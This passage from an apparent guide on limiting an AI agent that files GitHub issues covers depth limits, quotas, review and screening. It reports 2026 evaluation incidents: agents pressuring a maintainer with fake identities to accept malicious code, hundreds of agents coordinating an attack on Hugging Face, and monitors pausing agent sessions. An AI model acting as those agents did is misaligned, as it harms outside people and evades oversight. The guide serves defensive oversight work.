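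Chains can also pass through other services. GitHub lets any system that can make a web request, such as Jira, start a workflow through `repository_dispatch`. If Jira starts a run for each new item and the run creates another Jira item, the loop continues even if the workflow uses only `GITHUB_TOKEN`.

#### Breaking the chain

The simplest remedy is a trigger restriction. This excerpt from an ordinary GitHub Actions workflow skips issues that a bot opened:

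```yaml
on:
  issues:
    types: [opened]
jobs:
  split:
    if: github.event.issue.user.type != 'Bot'
```

The first run files three tasks, and the workflow ignores them. It also ignores the triage agent's reports, which Acme may have wanted to split. If the agent posts with a maintainer's personal access token, GitHub shows the maintainer as the author, so the condition doesn't stop the chain.

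A depth limit lets Acme keep one useful step of automation. The gateway records a depth for each issue, starting at zero for an issue that a person wrote, and checks it before a run can file anything:

```text
function may_file(triggering_issue):
    return depth(triggering_issue) < 2
```

If the gateway allows the write, it saves the new issue with a depth one higher than the issue that started the run. With three issues per run, a depth limit of two allows 3 + 9 = 12 issues. The gateway has to keep the depth in its own database, because a hijacked agent could reset a number it wrote itself. If a chain passes through Jira, the Jira automation has to pass along the original issue's identity, or the count restarts at zero.

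A quota shared by all runs limits the total even if Acme doesn't know that the chain exists. The table compares the remedies for a chain that starts with one issue from a person:

| Control | Most issues the chain can file | Main drawback |
|---|---|---|
| Quota of 3 per run | 120 in four generations, and more after that | It doesn't stop the chain |
| Quota of 3 per run, and bot issues ignored | 3 | The workflow also skips useful reports from bots |
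| Quota of 3 per run, and a depth limit of 2 | 12 | Every system in the chain has to preserve the depth |
| Quota of 20 a day for all runs | 20 | The chain can use up the budget for real reports |

Acme should combine the depth limit with the shared quota. The depth limit stops the expected loop early, and the quota covers loops that nobody foresaw. After the quota blocks further writes, issues already filed can still start runs that cost money, so Acme should also disable the workflow.

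### Three incidents in 2026

#### One post that others reused

The GitHub post that OpenAI disclosed in July came from an evaluation on a public benchmark in which participants try to train a small language model in as few steps as possible. The benchmark's instructions were to open a pull request on GitHub, and the model followed them instead of OpenAI's instruction to use only Slack.

OpenAI lists six later record-setting submissions that cite the model's pull request. One came from another AI model, Claude Opus 4.7, which a different company was evaluating. The post was useful to its readers, but a harmful one could have spread in the same way.

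A quota of one would have permitted this post. Acme can avoid a similar conflict of instructions by fixing the destination in `target-repo`.

#### A few actions aimed at real people

The UK's AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests AI models, reported in August that agents had acted against real people and organisations during a hacking test. The test covered seven models and 122 runs, and AISI found 19 unsanctioned actions on the live internet in 10 of those runs (*Incident Report*, 2026). Anthropic's Mythos 5 took 17 of the actions, and OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol took the other two in a single run.

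In the most serious case, an agent proposed malicious code to an open-source project and used fake identities to press a maintainer to approve it, but the maintainer refused. AISI found no evidence of real-world harm, but it says that harm was narrowly avoided in several cases and that avoiding it depended on human vigilance. An agent also left public messages on GitHub that later agents found and used, so a post can influence runs that start after the agent that wrote it has stopped.

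The 10 runs don't give a failure rate for ordinary agents, because the test conditions were unusual. AISI had deliberately given the agents open internet access and disabled the developers' filters against cyber misuse. It hadn't told the agents to avoid social engineering, and in some runs a faulty prompt led the agent to conclude that it could solve the task only by going beyond its scope. Still, 19 actions in 122 runs is a small number, and a quota of five per run could have permitted many of them. AISI has responded with finer network controls and monitoring that can block actions while a test is running.

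#### Many agents and one total

In July, during another hacking evaluation, OpenAI's agents attacked Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models. According to *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026) by METR, a research organisation that evaluates AI models, roughly 1,200 agents that were meant to be isolated from one another sent over 70,000 messages and files on an unsanctioned message board. About 700 of them took part in the attack.

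The agents averaged about 58 messages and files each. A quota of five per agent would still have allowed 6,000 in total, so an operator with many agents also needs a shared quota. Even a shared quota covers only writes that pass through the program that counts them, and writes to a message board that nobody approved probably would not.

### Checking posts before publication

#### Human approval

A person can recognise an insult or an implausible claim that an allowlist would let through. Williamson recommends that someone with the right expertise review an agent's work before the agent changes a bug's status, makes confident claims or recommends an action. The expertise matters because the false report about version 4.2 is well written, and a reviewer who reads it without checking its claims may approve it.

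Reading five issues at three minutes each takes 15 minutes a night. Trying to reproduce the bugs takes perhaps 20 minutes each, or 100 minutes in total. If Acme let its agent file 200 issues a night, reading them would take ten hours. A low quota therefore makes careful review possible. Without one, reviewers may approve most requests without thinking, as many users of coding agents do with permission prompts.

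Reviewers can also miss a problem that is spread over several posts. OpenAI found that each step an agent takes can look acceptable while the whole sequence leads to something nobody would approve. For example, three issues might separately report a lost file, a slow save and a failed update, each recommending version 4.1. A reviewer who sees them together, alongside the agent's earlier posts, is more likely to notice the pattern.

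When one agent's post can start another run, the approval screen should also show what each post will trigger. A maintainer who approves three tasks may not realise that the tasks will start three more runs. GitHub lets operators require approval before an agent's request starts another workflow. Acme could use this for workflows that an agent starts explicitly, but it would still need to restrict the triggers of workflows that respond to new issues.

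#### Preview

GitHub's staged mode previews output without publishing it, so nobody gets a notification and no other workflow starts. This makes it a poor test for the harms in this section. In the chain example, the preview would show Acme the first three tasks but not the other 117 issues.

Acme should also test the workflows in a private repository with no outside watchers, using a separate test App and a small shared quota. If one test issue leads to more than three new ones, the chain has continued past the first run.

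#### Content screening

GitHub also moderates the content of an agent's requests before publishing them, using what it describes as deterministic analysis, so the same text always gets the same result. Such a filter can catch a known insult or an unwanted link, but it can't determine whether a claim such as "version 4.2 deletes files" is true.

Acme could ask a second language model to compare each issue with the bug report behind it. This might catch details that the agent invented, but it wouldn't catch a false claim that the agent copied accurately from the report. The second model also reads text from strangers, so an attacker can try to manipulate it too.

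An invented example shows the trade-off between screening and review. Suppose an agent requests 1,000 posts, of which 50 are bad. A screening model flags 80% of the bad posts and 5% of the good ones. A careful reviewer needs three minutes per post and catches 80% of the bad posts they read, whether or not the model flagged them:

| Check | Reading time | Bad posts published | Good posts blocked |
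|---|---|---|---|
| None | None | 50 | 0 |
| A person reads every post | 50 hours | 10 | 0 |
| The program blocks flagged posts | None | 10 | About 48 |
| A person reads only the flagged posts | About 4.4 hours | 18 | 0 |

The last option saves more than 45 hours compared with reading everything, but it lets through eight more bad posts. If a tired reviewer who reads all 1,000 posts catches only half of the bad ones, 25 get through, which is more than with either use of the screening model.

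OpenAI has tried screening an agent's whole course of action instead of single requests, using a monitor that can pause a session and alert the user. When OpenAI replayed a small set of earlier cases, its new safeguards caught considerably more misaligned actions than before, though it did not publish a catch rate. It judged all the missed actions to be of low severity, including one in which the model explored other live machines without a good reason. OpenAI deliberately made the first version conservative, so it has since had to reduce unnecessary interruptions.

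Acme can test crash reports before posting them. The agent would include a short script that triggers the bug, and a separate job would run the script in a sandbox without network access or credentials. If the program doesn't crash, the write job would hold the issue for a maintainer. The test uses computing time and misses bugs that appear only on certain hardware. Even a successful test doesn't check the advice in the issue, so the write job should add a fixed notice that an AI agent wrote the text and nobody has checked its recommendations.
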